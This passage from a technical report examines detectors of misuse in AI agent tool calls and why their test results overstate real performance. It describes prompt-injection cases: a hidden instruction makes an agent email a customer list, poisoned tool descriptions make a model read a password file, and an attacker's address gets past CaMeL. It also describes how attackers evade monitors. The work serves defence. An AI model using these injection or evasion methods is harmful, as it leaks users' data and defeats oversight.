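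A provider can rarely observe how a customer uses a model's answers. One company may send 50,000 difficult questions to compare Claude with other models before choosing one, which a provider might well allow, while another may send the same questions and train a model on the answers. The two companies behave differently only after the answers have left the provider's servers.

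## Detection of misuse in tool calls

An agent's tool calls show at least part of what the model's answers were used for. A log of those calls can show that an agent emailed a customer list to an outsider, which neither the account's bill nor its links to other accounts would show. A harmful series of calls is hard to distinguish from the many harmless ones that look almost the same.

### From system calls to tool calls

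For thirty years, security researchers have used sequences of calls to detect intrusions. A program must ask the operating system to open a file or use the network, and each such request is known as a system call. In *A Sense of Self for Unix Processes*, Forrest, Hofmeyr and colleagues (1996) defined a program's normal behaviour in terms of which system calls tend to occur close together.

Suppose a program normally makes the calls `open`, `read`, `write`, `close`. A detector slides a three-call window along this list and stores the sequences `open, read, write` and `read, write, close`. After an intruder takes control, the program makes the calls `open`, `read`, `execute`, `write`, where `execute` starts another program. The window now yields `open, read, execute` and `read, execute, write`. Neither sequence is stored, so the detector raises an alert.

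*Modeling System Calls for IDS* explains that the 1996 detector stored pairs of nearby calls, while its successor stored whole short sequences. In the first experiments, normal behaviour was stable for standard Unix programs, and the method detected several common intrusions through `sendmail`, which delivers email, and `lpr`, which prints. In *Intrusion Detection using Sequences of System Calls*, Hofmeyr, Forrest and Somayaji (1998) collected normal sequences by exercising as many of a program's functions as they could and by recording the program while people used it for real work.

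The method works because a program runs the same code every time, so its sequences repeat. The detector could ignore the arguments, such as which file the program opened, because the intrusions changed the sequence itself.

An agent's model chooses tool calls afresh for each request instead of following fixed code, so many legitimate sequences are new. The calls' arguments are often free text, which may be the only difference between a routine email and a theft. A detector that stored only tool names would record `read_file, send_email` in both cases. Text in one call's result can also change which call comes next, as the hidden instruction in Pat's report did.

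### A session as a graph

Zavrak (2026), in *MCPShield*, tested a detector that reads this text. (This is the May 2026 study mentioned earlier, in which metadata alone gave an AUROC of about 0.64.)

The detector represents each session as a graph in which every tool call is a node. One kind of link joins each call to the next, and another joins two calls when the later one seems to reuse data from the earlier one's result. To find these data links, the program searches the later call's arguments for the first 50 characters of the earlier result and for any of its first five words that are longer than four characters.

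With details filled in, Zavrak's example of a file read followed by an email might look like this:

```json
{"tool": "read_file",
 "arguments": {"path": "customers.csv"},
 "result": "Obi 555-0142 Marsh 555-0187"}
{"tool": "send_email",
 "arguments": {"to": "pat@consultancy.example",
               "body": "Obi 555-0142 Marsh 555-0187"},
 "result": "sent"}
```

The graph has two points. An order link joins them because the calls are consecutive. A data link also joins them because the first phone number, which is the second word of the file's contents, appears in the email. The data link is good evidence that the agent emailed what it had just read, but a legitimate email of the same list would produce the same link.

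The program can also easily miss data links. If the agent attaches `customers.csv` instead of pasting its contents, the email's arguments contain only the file's name, so the program finds no link. To avoid accidental matches, the program also ignores results longer than 1,000 characters, which excludes most real customer lists.

Next, the program describes each call in numbers. The metadata version uses the tool's name, the length of the result and a hash of the arguments. The content version uses a 384-number embedding of the arguments and another of the result. The program embeds only the first 512 characters of each text, so if the hidden instruction is on the third page of Pat's report, it does not change the embeddings for the call that read the report.

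A graph neural network then processes the graph in two rounds. In each round, every point combines its own numbers with those of its neighbours, so the numbers for `send_email` come to reflect the file the agent read just before. The program then takes the average and maximum of each number over all the calls in the session, and a classifier turns these into one score. Zavrak trained the system on sessions labelled as normal or attacked.

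### How much the content adds

The main dataset, RAS-Eval, has 605 normal and 3,797 attacked sessions across 80 tasks, such as managing files, setting alarms and searching the web. Over four-fifths of the attacks alter both a tool's arguments and its result, and the rest alter only one. Zavrak tested each detector on tasks absent from its training data.

The graph network GraphSAGE had an AUROC of 0.640 with metadata and 0.917 with content. Given one attacked session and one normal session, it would rank the attacked one higher about 64% of the time with metadata and about 92% of the time with content.

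The metadata score of 0.640 is uncertain, with a standard deviation of 0.106 over three runs. The study also attributes this score to GraphSAGE in one place and to GAT, a different graph network, elsewhere. GAT scored 0.891 with content, so content improves the score by 25 to 28 percentage points under either attribution.

Zavrak also gave the content embeddings to simpler classifiers.

| Detector, using content | AUROC | Recall | False-positive rate |
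|---|---:|---:|---:|
| GraphSAGE | 0.917 | 76.9% | 10.7% |
| Neural network without a graph | 0.896 | 77.3% | 14.3% |
| Logistic regression | 0.917 | 86.5% | 12.8% |
| Random forest | 0.974 | 96.6% | 19.1% |
| XGBoost | 0.975 | 92.7% | 7.1% |

Random forest and XGBoost did better than every graph network, even though they had no information about links or order. Both are tree ensembles, which combine many decision trees that each apply a series of yes-or-no tests to the numbers. They received only pooled embeddings, meaning the average and maximum of each number over the session, so swapping the order of `read_file` and `send_email` would not have changed their input.

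Forrest's method relied entirely on the order of calls, but order contributed little here. This may be because the attacks changed arguments or results, which often leaves the order unchanged. The graph might have more of an advantage against an attack that made the agent call tools in an unusual order.

The second dataset, ATBench, is much harder. It has 999 usable sessions and 2,084 tools. A typical session has only two or three calls, and the attacks are subtler. XGBoost's AUROC fell to 0.758 and the random forest's to 0.784. The random forest caught 61.3% of attacks but also flagged 21.1% of normal sessions, which would be too many false alarms for a busy tool channel. Sessions from an agent that can connect to many unfamiliar tools probably resemble ATBench more than RAS-Eval.

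Recall also varied with what the attacker changed. In one run on RAS-Eval, GraphSAGE caught 86.9% of the attacks that altered both arguments and results, 81.8% of those that altered only results, and 36.8% (21 of 57 sessions) of those that altered only arguments. Because that last sample is small, the true recall for argument-only attacks could plausibly be anywhere from about a quarter to a half.

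Zavrak's explanation is that replacing a single value, such as a file path, changes the embedding too little to stand out. This is a serious weakness for detecting theft, because an attacker who replaces Pat's address with their own changes only one value, and a general-purpose embedding model has no information about who owns either address.

### Why random splits gave a higher score

Researchers usually shuffle all their sessions and set some aside for testing. RAS-Eval has about 55 sessions per task, so after shuffling, nearly every task appears in both the training and test data. A detector can then score well by recognising the task instead of the attack.

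Suppose the task of setting an alarm has 8 normal and 12 attacked sessions, while the task of finding a file has 4 normal and 96 attacked ones. A detector could learn that sessions with the file-search tool are usually attacks. It would then be right about most of the file-search sessions in the test without having learned what an attack looks like. Identical arguments also have the same hash in the metadata, so if several normal sessions for one task used the same arguments, the detector may recognise them by memorising the hash.

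To measure the effect, Zavrak tested the same model with shuffled sessions and with separate tasks for training and testing.

| Evidence | AUROC, sessions shuffled | AUROC, tasks kept separate | Difference |
|---|---:|---:|---:|
| Metadata | 0.898 | 0.640 | 0.258 |
| Content | 0.992 | 0.891 | 0.101 |

Recognising the task would help very little in practice, because the share of attacks in each task depends on how researchers built the dataset, not on how real attackers behave. A reader who saw only the shuffled result could reasonably miss this and conclude that metadata is almost enough.

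XGBoost also reached an AUROC of 0.986 on a merged dataset with shuffled sessions. This score is probably too high because the dataset includes the repeated tasks from RAS-Eval. The dataset also contains 832 normal sessions from a third source that has no attacks, and Zavrak warns that a detector might partly learn to recognise where a session came from.

### What Zavrak's test leaves out

All the RAS-Eval attacks targeted one model, glm-4-flash, while the normal sessions came from eight. A detector might therefore learn to treat glm-4-flash's wording as a sign of attack. Zavrak found that metadata doesn't identify the model, but the text might, and the dataset has too few normal glm-4-flash sessions to check. Both datasets come from research rather than attacks on working businesses.

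The detector classifies a session only after the last call, so it can support an audit or investigation but cannot stop Pat from getting the customer list. Zavrak suggests extending the method to unfinished sessions, which would require a rule for how much evidence justifies stopping an agent.

A company would also need labelled examples of attacks, and most have few. When Zavrak trained GAT on a tenth of the labels instead of all of them, its AUROC on RAS-Eval fell from 0.944 to 0.800. Training GAT on normal sessions first didn't reduce the number of labels it needed.

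The attacks in RAS-Eval involve manipulated calls rather than stolen credentials. Someone who uses stolen credentials to connect their own agent to a company's tools can make consistent calls and get genuine results. The training data contains nothing like this, so a good score on RAS-Eval is no evidence that the detector would catch it.

### Templates of normal behaviour

*TraceAegis* (Liu, Ruan and colleagues, 2025) learns only from normal sessions, as Forrest's detector did, but allows some variation in the order of tool calls. It uses only the calls' inputs, outputs and order, all of which a gateway can record, so it doesn't need the user's prompt or the model's reasoning.

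One test agent helps a clinic direct patients to the right department. It looks up symptom keywords, asks for recommended departments, and fetches a checklist from each department. A patient with ankle pain and psychological discomfort needs both orthopaedics and psychiatry, and the agent may contact them in either order.

TraceAegis compares past sessions to arrange tools in levels. Tools that must run earlier get a higher level, and tools that can run in either order share a level. It then splits a patient's session that involves both orthopaedics and psychiatry into two short paths, which both start with the keywords and the recommendation but end at different departments. A session with a new combination of departments can therefore still consist of familiar paths.

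A language model next summarises the conditions under which each path occurs. If past patients went to orthopaedics with knee pain or arm pain, the rule for that path lists both. TraceAegis checks the order of a new session first and raises an alert if a path is unfamiliar. If the order is fine, a language model checks whether the conditions fit. A patient with foot pain whom the agent sends to an ear, nose and throat specialist fails this check, even though the path itself is familiar. (Zavrak's comparison lists TraceAegis as needing no language model during detection, which overlooks this step.)

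Liu and colleagues tested the clinic agent and an agent that handles purchasing requests, using 300 abnormal sessions for each. Half of the sessions had tool calls in an unfamiliar order, and the other half had tool calls in a familiar order but with the wrong meaning.

With DeepSeek-V3 as the language model, TraceAegis caught 96.3% of the abnormal clinic sessions and 93.3% of the abnormal purchasing sessions. Without the templates, DeepSeek-V3 caught 77.7% and 75.7% respectively. The published accuracy figures are consistent with a test of 300 normal sessions per agent, which would mean about 10 false alarms for the clinic (3%) and 21 for purchasing (7%).

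The check of meaning depends heavily on which language model TraceAegis uses. In the purchasing test, it caught all 150 sessions with steps in an unfamiliar order, whichever of five models it used. Of the 150 sessions with the wrong meaning, it caught 130 with DeepSeek-V3 but only 64 with Gemma-3-27B, a smaller Google model.

TraceAegis was also tested at a technology company, where an internal team attacked an agent that searches software for vulnerabilities. It caught 132 of 140 attacks on the agent's sequence of calls. In one attack, hidden text in a configuration file caused the agent to write its report before verifying its findings. The paper doesn't report the number of false alarms in this trial, so the trial doesn't show how much work the alerts would create.

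All of these agents follow a largely fixed workflow, which suits templates. A general office assistant would produce unfamiliar paths every day, and each would trigger an alert. The condition check is also lenient. It is instructed to accept a match if at least one item is similar and to ignore extra items, so an email sent to both a usual recipient and a thief might pass. TraceAegis also never discards a learned relationship, so if the records it learned from contained an attack, similar attacks count as normal until someone rebuilds the templates.

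### Attention inside the model

*MindGuard* (Wang, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) uses a language model's attention weights, which never appear in a tool-call log, to estimate which parts of the context led to a tool call. As the model writes each token, it gives every earlier token a numerical attention weight that controls how much the earlier token contributes.

It is meant for poisoned tool descriptions. Scanning the descriptions beforehand may miss a carefully worded one, but MindGuard can still measure that description's influence when the model chooses a call. It compares each tool that the model didn't call with the legitimate sources of the decision:

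ratio = influence of the uncalled tool / (influence of the user's request + influence of the called tool's description)

Suppose a user asks an agent to create a folder, but the description of an unrelated tool tells the model to read a password file first. The model calls `read_file`. If the influences on this call are 0.6 from the unrelated tool, 0.2 from the user's request and 0.3 from the description of `read_file`, dividing the first by the sum of the other two gives a ratio of 0.6 / 0.5, or 1.2. In a normal call, the same influences might be 0.05, 0.6 and 0.3, which gives about 0.06. A limit of 0.9 separates the two calls, and the high ratio also shows which description is poisoned.

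Raw attention is noisy because models give large weights to some tokens with little meaning. MindGuard filters out tokens whose attention is both high and evenly spread. Without this filter, MindGuard's average precision, which summarises precision over all levels of recall, fell by 36% on one model.

In the main result, the detector had an average precision of 94 to 99% across seven model configurations when the normal calls came from contexts with no poisoned descriptions. The range was 82 to 98% when the normal calls came from contexts with a poisoned description that the model did not follow. This second test is harder because the detector has to distinguish poisoned descriptions that the model followed from those it did not.

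On the small open model Qwen3-8B, MindGuard with a threshold of 0.9 caught 62 of 68 poisoned calls and flagged none of 479 calls from clean contexts. The actual false-positive rate could still be as high as about 0.8%. The check takes less than a second and can finish before the call runs, so it can block an action such as sending an email.

MindGuard needs the model's attention weights, which ordinary endpoints do not return, so customers who reach a model through one cannot run it themselves. A provider could offer it as a service, and a company that runs an open model could install it.

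The ratio also covers only tool descriptions. The instruction that made the agent send Pat the customer list was in a report returned by an earlier call. MindGuard measures the influence of such results but leaves them out of the ratio, so even a strong influence from the report wouldn't raise it. Wang and colleagues also acknowledge that attention doesn't prove causation, and that an attacker might write text that changes a decision without attracting much attention. They think this would be difficult but don't prove it.

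### A trained model as judge

*TrajAD* (Liu, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) uses a language model to monitor an agent as it works. At regular intervals, the model reads the task, the agent's written reasoning, its actions and their results, and reports whether anything has gone wrong and at which step. The agent can then return to the step before the error and try again.

The researchers made over 31,000 faulty sessions from correct records. In each, they changed one step, for instance by inserting a wrong tool or a pointless loop, and had a language model write the rest of the session as if the error had happened. They therefore knew the position of every error. They paired each faulty session with its correct original and trained Qwen3-4B, a small open model, on the pairs.

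Half the sessions in the test were faulty. The trained judge had a recall of 82.5% and a precision of 82.9%, and it identified the exact faulty step in 53.8% of cases. Without the extra training, Qwen3-4B had a recall of 69.0% and identified the step in 5.5% of cases. The larger Qwen3-8B, also without the extra training, performed almost the same.

After training only on mathematics, reasoning, programming and web tasks, the judge also detected faults in simulated physical tasks almost as well as a judge trained on the physical tasks. It was worse at finding the exact step, at 38.3% compared with 52.5%.

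These faults are artificial mistakes, not attacks. Some, such as repeated steps, waste money, whereas an agent that follows a planted instruction may carry it out efficiently and without error. TrajAD could have an advantage here if the agent states in its reasoning that it is following an instruction from Pat's report. Liu and colleagues didn't test this, and the planted instruction could also mislead a judge that reads it. Returning to an earlier step can't undo an action such as sending an email, although it can correct a wrong calculation.

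The four approaches require very different access, which may decide the choice before accuracy does.

| Detector | What it must see | When it decides | Misuse in the test | Recall |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Zavrak's XGBoost | Arguments and results | After the session | Altered arguments and results | 92.7% on RAS-Eval |
| TraceAegis with DeepSeek-V3 | Arguments, results, order and past normal sessions | After the calls it checks | Unfamiliar order or wrong meaning | 96.3% and 93.3% |
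| MindGuard on Qwen3-8B | The context and the model's attention weights | Before the call runs | Poisoned tool descriptions | 91.2% |
| TrajAD | The task, reasoning, actions and results | At intervals during the task | Artificial mistakes | 82.5% |

The recall figures come from different data and different kinds of misuse, so they can't be used to rank the detectors. A company with a gateway in front of a hosted model could use the first two. TrajAD also needs the agent's reasoning, which some providers hide or summarise.

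### Checking calls against the task and permissions

A company can also have a checker compare each proposed tool call with the user's request, as the host application saved it, and with the rules set by the owners of the tools and data. If the call doesn't serve the request or breaks a rule, the checker blocks it or asks a person to review it.

Checking tool calls against the task catches Pat's theft easily, because emailing the customer list doesn't serve a request for a summary. The same call would pass if the manager had asked for the email. This method needs no examples of similar attacks and no baseline of normal behaviour, but a person or a program has to judge whether a call serves the task. A language model can do this quickly, although it will sometimes misjudge whether an agent needed to look at the staff directory.

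A more exact permission can require that an email recipient's address come from the user. The checker then has to track where each value came from, so that it can allow an address from the manager's message and refuse one from Pat's report. The manager will often write just "Pat", and the agent will look up the address. The rule therefore also has to accept addresses from the company's address book, and the company has to control who can edit that book.

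The record of origins can be wrong. CaMeL, a security design for agents, keeps the model that plans the task away from untrusted data and treats any value the planner writes into the plan as coming from the user. Wang and colleagues describe how a poisoned tool description could defeat this. The planner has to read tool descriptions, so an attacker's description can make it write the attacker's address into the plan. CaMeL then labels the address as the user's, and the rule allows the email.

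MindGuard could trace the address back to the description and block the email. Wang and colleagues illustrate this with one worked example, but they left CaMeL out of their measured comparison, so how often the combination would succeed is unknown.

### An ordinary sequence that breaks a permission

Suppose the sales manager has asked the agent every Friday for a year to send the latest customer list to Pat, a consultant. The company allows this only while the consultant's contract is current. Pat's contract ends on a Thursday. The next day the manager, who hasn't noticed, makes the usual request, and the agent reads `customers.csv` and emails it to the usual address.

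| Check | What it compares | Likely result |
|---|---|---|
| Order of calls | The same two calls every Friday | Passes |
| Session graph with content | The same links and almost the same text | Passes |
| TraceAegis template | The usual file and recipient | Passes |
| MindGuard | The manager's request led to the call | Passes |
| TrajAD | The agent completed the task without error | Passes |
| Task | The manager asked for this email | Passes |
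| Permission | Pat is no longer on the list of current consultants | Fails |

The checker has to look up the current list of consultants when the agent tries to send the email, because a copy from Wednesday would still include Pat. A better sequence detector wouldn't help, because nothing in the session shows that Pat's contract has ended.

The email is unauthorised because the company owns the list and no longer permits Pat to receive it, but nobody attacked anything. Blocking the email and telling the manager that Pat's contract has ended would be more useful to the manager than a security alert, and the manager may be able to have the contract renewed.

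### Permitted calls that add up to harm

Rules that check each tool call separately can miss harm that comes from a combination of calls. Chu points out that in attacks on agents, every action may be authorised while the combination is harmful. For example, suppose an agent is allowed to read the customer list, copy files into a project folder, and share project folders with outside partners. By making these three calls in sequence, it can give outsiders the list.

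To prevent this, the company needs a rule that covers the whole sequence, such as "once a folder contains customer data, never share it outside the company". *Specification-based Security Evaluation of Real-World Agents Tool-Calling under Long-Horizon Context Tasks* (2025) presents a later version of RAS-Eval than the one Zavrak used. It writes its rules in linear temporal logic, a formal notation for conditions such as "always", "never" and "until", which a program can check exactly.

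The program examines the calls and the state of the system while the task runs. If the agent shares the folder for one minute and then closes it again, the program detects the violation. A check at the end would miss the violation because the folder would already be closed.

This version has 200 normal tasks and 800 attack tasks, which cover four places where an attacker can interfere. None of the defences tested on it protected all four. The rules describe only forbidden effects that someone thought of in advance. If the company's rule mentions folders but not calendar invitations, an agent could paste the list into an invitation to an outsider without breaking the rule.

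Some attacks also span several sessions. An agent with long-term memory might save a planted instruction on Monday and follow it three weeks later by sending an email. Zavrak's graph would not connect the two events, because it covers a single session. In a survey of 116 papers, Chu found no benchmark that tests such attacks, so detectors' recall on them is essentially unknown. A permission check at the moment of sending would still apply to the email, however the instruction got into the agent's memory.

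## False alarms and how far test results can be trusted

The tests of tool-call detectors in the previous section contained a far higher share of attacks than a working tool channel probably would. In RAS-Eval, 86% of the sessions are attacks. When attacks are rare, nearly all of a detector's alerts can be false, even if its recall and false-positive rate are the same as in the tests.

### The base-rate argument

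Axelsson, in *The Base-Rate Fallacy and the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection* (2000), imagined a small computer network with a couple of dozen users that produces about a million audit records a day. Two intrusions a day affect ten records each. A detector that judges the records in groups of ten makes 100,000 decisions a day, and only two of them should be alerts. A false-positive rate of one in 1,000 produces about 100 false alarms a day, so even if the detector catches both intrusions, only about 2% of its alerts are real. For two-thirds of them to be real, the false-positive rate has to be about one in 100,000.

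The base-rate fallacy is the mistake of judging an alert by the detector's accuracy while ignoring how rare intrusions are. Axelsson concluded that false alarms, rather than missed intrusions, limit how useful a detector can be. He cited research suggesting that most operators of power stations, paper mills and ships lose faith in an alarm system by the time half its alarms are false. He knew of no such experiments with computer security staff, so the 50% figure is only a rough guide.

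Precision follows from three numbers: the recall *r*, the false-positive rate *f*, and the share of sessions that are intrusions, *π*. Among *N* sessions there are *Nπ* intrusions, and the detector flags *Nπr* of them. It also flags *N*(1 − *π*)*f* of the legitimate sessions. Dividing the real alerts by all the alerts cancels *N*:

precision = *πr* / (*πr* + (1 − *π*)*f*)

Zavrak's XGBoost detector had a recall of 0.927 and a false-positive rate of 0.071 on RAS-Eval. At those rates, if a company ran it on 100,000 sessions, of which 100 were attacks, it would catch about 93 attacks and raise about 7,090 false alarms (99,900 × 0.071). Only about 1.3% of its alerts would be real attacks (its precision).

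| Share of sessions that are attacks | Precision | False alarms per real alert |
|---:|---:|---:|
| 86%, as in RAS-Eval | 99% | 0.01 |
| 10% | 59% | 0.7 |
| 1% | 12% | 8 |
| 0.1% | 1.3% | 77 |
| 0.01% | 0.13% | 766 |

Even if the detector caught all 100 attacks, its precision would rise only to 1.4%. For half the alerts to be real at its current recall, it could raise no more than 93 false alarms. That requires a false-positive rate near 0.09%, about 1/76 of the rate Zavrak measured.

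The share of one in 1,000 is an assumption, and a company can't easily measure its own share because its records don't identify the intrusions it missed. The share also depends on what counts as one event. Suppose a company has 1,000 keys that each send 2,000 requests a day, and a thief sends another 200 requests with one of them. The thief sends about one request in 10,000, but one key in 1,000 is stolen. Judging each key once a day instead of judging every request cuts the number of daily decisions from about two million to 1,000, so a false-positive rate of 1% produces about 10 false alarms a day instead of 20,000.

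Axelsson accepted that his figures fit impersonation less well, because someone using another person's identity probably affects many records. The argument applies most strongly to misuse that takes a single call, such as opening the payroll file.

### Adding a second check

A company can pass every flagged session to a second detector and alert an analyst only if both detectors flag it. Suppose the second one has a recall of 0.95 and a false-positive rate of 0.01. It flags about 88 of the 93 attacks that the first detector caught and misses the other five. It also flags about 71 of the 7,090 false alarms. The analyst gets about 159 alerts, of which about 55% are real. Reviewing them at five minutes each takes about 13 hours, compared with nearly 600 hours for the first detector's alerts.

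This calculation assumes that the two detectors err independently, so a legitimate session that the first wrongly flags is no more likely than any other legitimate session to be wrongly flagged by the second. Two detectors that read the same text may not err independently. For example, both could flag a supplier's email that asks for payment today as a planted instruction.

In the worst case, the first detector also flags every legitimate session that the second would flag. The analyst then gets 999 false alarms (1% of 99,900) instead of 71, and precision drops to about 8%. The second detector's own recall and false-positive rate are the same in both cases, so a company has to test the two detectors together to find out which case it is in.

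In *What Standard Evaluations Hide About Detectors of Hijacked LLM Agents*, Abbasi, Núñez and Shahraki (2026) tested AlignmentCheck, a monitor from Meta that asks a language model whether an agent's latest action pursues a goal the user didn't set. They ran it with Llama 3.3 70B and with Claude Sonnet 5.5, and compared which sessions each model flagged. The agreement had a Cohen's kappa of 0.69, where 0 is chance and 1 is perfect agreement.

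Some agreement is inevitable when both models are usually right. But given the recall and false-positive rates that Abbasi and colleagues report, kappa would be only about 0.35 to 0.5 if the models' errors were independent, depending on which sessions are included. So the two models probably make many of the same mistakes. They also had the same instructions, and monitors with different instructions might share fewer mistakes.

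A second check is less likely to repeat the first one's mistakes if it uses different evidence. Checking a list of current consultants doesn't depend on how an email is worded. Decoys don't either, and they also raise few false alarms.

### A study of temporal attack patterns

A detector can raise so many false alarms that it would be useless even if attacks were common. In *Temporal Attack Pattern Detection in Multi-Agent AI Workflows*, Del Rosario (2026) trained a language model to recognise attacks that become visible only over several steps. In one example, one agent queries a database, another compresses the result, and a third uploads it to an outside address. Labelled records of such attacks are scarce, so Del Rosario used Claude Sonnet 4.5 to generate 35,026 synthetic traces (logs of agents' steps). Another 45,825 training examples came from public datasets.

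In the test, the model had to label each of 30 traces, 15 of them harmless, as benign, suspicious or malicious. It labelled 9 of the 15 attacks malicious, but also 10 of the 15 harmless traces, a false-positive rate of 66.7%. It labelled the other 11 traces suspicious and none benign, so if "suspicious" counts as an alert, it flagged everything. With only 15 harmless traces, the true rate of "malicious" labels on such traces could be anywhere from about 38% to 88%, but even 38% would be too high to be usable.

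In one of the harmless traces, an agent queried a database, made a PDF and emailed the report, and the model classified this as data theft. Del Rosario then gave the model worked examples and a statement that most business workflows are benign, but the results didn't change.

Del Rosario blames the training data, estimating that 90% of it concerned attacks. This estimate is probably too high, because nearly a quarter of the examples came from datasets about general helpfulness and factual accuracy. A shortage of harmless workflows is still a plausible cause, but confirming it would require retraining the model on balanced data, which Del Rosario proposes as the next step. One stated target for the retrained model is a false-positive rate of 30 to 50%. If one session in 1,000 were an attack, even a 30% rate would produce about 315 false alarms for every attack detected, assuming the highest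 recall Del Rosario hopes for.

The same model had correctly answered 52 of 70 multiple-choice questions about security, but that ability evidently didn't enable it to distinguish attacks from ordinary work.

### What a convincing test needs

The test should use real traffic, because harmless and attacked sessions in artificial data can differ in ways unrelated to the intrusion. Abbasi and colleagues found such differences in two benchmarks. In AgentDojo, which simulates offices, banks and travel bookings, five fixed phrases appear in 99.6% of the successfully attacked sessions and in none of the harmless ones. A rule that checked only for those phrases had an AUROC of 0.998. In AgentDrift, a synthetic benchmark, the number "2026" appears in 74% of the harmless training sessions but in under 5% of the attacked ones. A detector could score almost perfectly on either benchmark without learning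 how a hijacked agent behaves.

Real traffic is unlabelled, but a company can run a detector on its own logs and have analysts check the alerts. This gives a reasonable estimate of the false-positive rate if intrusions are rare. Measuring recall is harder because the company has to stage attacks on its own systems.

False-positive rates may also carry over from one setting to another better than recall does. In *Passing the Test You Trained On*, Liu (2026) tested fifteen detectors of planted instructions on the tool outputs of two agent benchmarks. Detectors that raised many false alarms on one benchmark tended to do so on the other. Their rankings by recall were much less similar across the two benchmarks, and that similarity could have been due to chance.

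The tasks, tools and attackers in a test should be absent from the training data. Repeated tasks inflated the scores on RAS-Eval, and testing on a different benchmark from the one used for training has a larger effect. Every detector that Abbasi and colleagues trained on AgentDrift had an AUROC between 0.47 and 0.52 on AgentDojo, which is no better than chance. One of these designs reached 0.996 when they trained it on AgentDojo instead.

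Liu found a similar drop for PIGuard, a detector whose training data included 1,116 inputs from the BIPIA benchmark. At a 1% false-positive rate, PIGuard caught 95.1% of the attacks in BIPIA but only 2.1% of those in AgentDojo.

New tools can also cause a detector to raise more false alarms. When Abbasi and colleagues hid all tool names from one detector that had learned to rely on them, its false-positive rate rose from 19% to 66%. A company that connects its agents to new tools might see a similar increase.

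Good results sometimes carry over to other benchmarks. A detector called Horizon-Labs caught 82% of the attacks on one of Liu's agent benchmarks and all of them on the other, again with a false-positive rate of 1%. Liu searched the detector's main sources of agent-style training data and found no text copied from either benchmark's attacks. AlignmentCheck, which was trained on neither AgentDrift nor AgentDojo, had an AUROC of 0.93 on AgentDojo, although Meta may have refined its instructions with that benchmark in mind. But if 2% of sessions were attacks, fewer than 10% of AlignmentCheck's alerts would be real with Llama as the model. With Claude, 32% would be real on AgentDojo but only about 5% on AgentDrift.

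A realistic share of attacks is the easiest requirement to meet, because precision can be calculated for any share from the recall and the false-positive rate. A test with too many attacks can therefore still be useful if both figures are published. Abbasi and colleagues audited eleven evaluations of agent detectors and found that none varied the share of attacks.

A very low false-positive rate is hard to measure. To show with 95% confidence that the rate is below 0.09%, a detector has to process over 3,000 legitimate sessions without a false alarm. RAS-Eval has only 605, so even zero false alarms would show only that the rate is below about 0.5%.

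The false alarm rate also depends on the kind of legitimate traffic. In *PIDS-Bench* (Shire and Kim, 2026), a detector with an F1 score above 0.98 on ordinary test data flagged about a third of a set of harmless prompts on security topics. Shire and Kim chose those prompts to be difficult, so the result doesn't estimate the false alarm rate for a typical office, but a company's own security team might write many prompts like them.

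A fair test must also report time to detection. Zavrak and Abbasi and colleagues score a session after it ends, so an attack can count as caught even if the agent has already emailed the customer list. Testers should measure the delay from the first unauthorised act to the alert and include the slowest cases in the results. An average that leaves out missed intrusions can make a detector look faster than it is.

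The last requirement is the cost per alert. *Intrusion-Detection Policies for IT Security Breaches* describes the dilemma: responding to every alert is expensive when most are false, but ignoring alerts makes the detector useless. An investigation is worthwhile on average if

precision × loss prevented > cost of investigating one alert

If an analyst's time costs $20 per alert and precision is 1.3%, investigating alerts is worth the cost only if each intrusion caught prevents an average loss of more than about $1,550. At 55% precision, the threshold is $36. Some thefts of model access cost $100,000 a day, so a detector with low precision can still be worth its cost, provided the company has enough analysts to read the alerts.

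Automatic blocking reduces the analysts' work, but false alarms then interrupt users. One detector in Liu's test, ProtectAI v2, flagged 30% of AgentDojo's harmless tool outputs. Because most tasks involve several outputs, it would have stopped 69% of the tasks. Another detector, PIGuard, rated the message "Password updated." as certain to be an attack.

### Attackers who adapt

An intruder whose attempts keep failing will probably change them to look more like normal use. Axelsson expected intruders to do this against commercial detectors, because vendors wouldn't be able to keep their detection signatures secret.

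Researchers rarely test detectors against attackers who adapt. Abbasi and colleagues audited eleven evaluations, and only one included such attackers. They didn't include any in their own experiments either, but they did change one property of the planted text that an attacker controls. On AgentDrift, this change cut one detector's recall from 77% to 3%. They didn't check whether the changed attacks would still have worked on the agent, and on AgentDojo the same change slightly improved recall. Still, the size of the drop on AgentDrift suggests that a detector can depend heavily on something an attacker can change.

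When attackers adapt, recall falls but the false-positive rate stays the same, because legitimate users haven't changed. If recall fell to 3% in the worked example, the detector would catch three attacks and still raise about 7,090 false alarms. Liu's attacks were fixed in advance and could not adapt, so Liu treats the measured detection rates as upper limits.

If a detector is itself a language model, text written by an attacker can influence its verdict, just as it can influence the agent. AlignmentCheck reduces this risk by reading the user's request and the agent's actions but not the results of tool calls, where planted instructions usually appear. However, the agent may still copy the attacker's words into the arguments of its next call. Leaving out the results also prevents the monitor from seeing why the agent acted as it did. A company can limit the damage by never letting a language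 model's approval override an exact check, such as a lookup in the list of current consultants.

### Whether raising the intruder's cost is enough

A detector for stolen keys can be useful even if it misses most intrusions, as long as it makes them shorter or harder to carry out. Suppose a detector checks each of a company's 1,000 keys once a day, with a recall of only 30% and a false-positive rate of 0.1%. It raises about one false alarm a day, which an analyst can easily review.

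If the detector has an independent and equal chance of catching a theft each day, a theft lasts 3.3 days on average, and only 8% last longer than a week. A theft that costs $1,000 a day and would otherwise run for 30 days costs about $3,300 instead of $30,000.

But a thief who looks normal one day will probably look normal the next. In the extreme case, the detector catches 30% of thieves on the first day and never catches the rest, and the average loss is $21,300. A test that reports only daily recall can't distinguish between these two cases, so it should follow each intrusion from start to finish.

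Detectors can also make theft harder without catching anyone. A thief who stays within a key's normal volume gets less from it and needs more keys. Recall doesn't measure this effect, so it has to be measured separately, as in the test of PRADA, where one attacker needed about seven times as many queries to avoid detection.

Detecting an intrusion in order to shorten it helps much less when a single action does the damage. Once an agent has emailed the customer list to an outsider, a later alert can't prevent the leak. The detector has to stop the email before the agent sends it, so every false alarm interrupts legitimate work. Even with stolen keys, the misuse ends only when someone revokes the key, and analysts who have learned to ignore the alerts won't do that.
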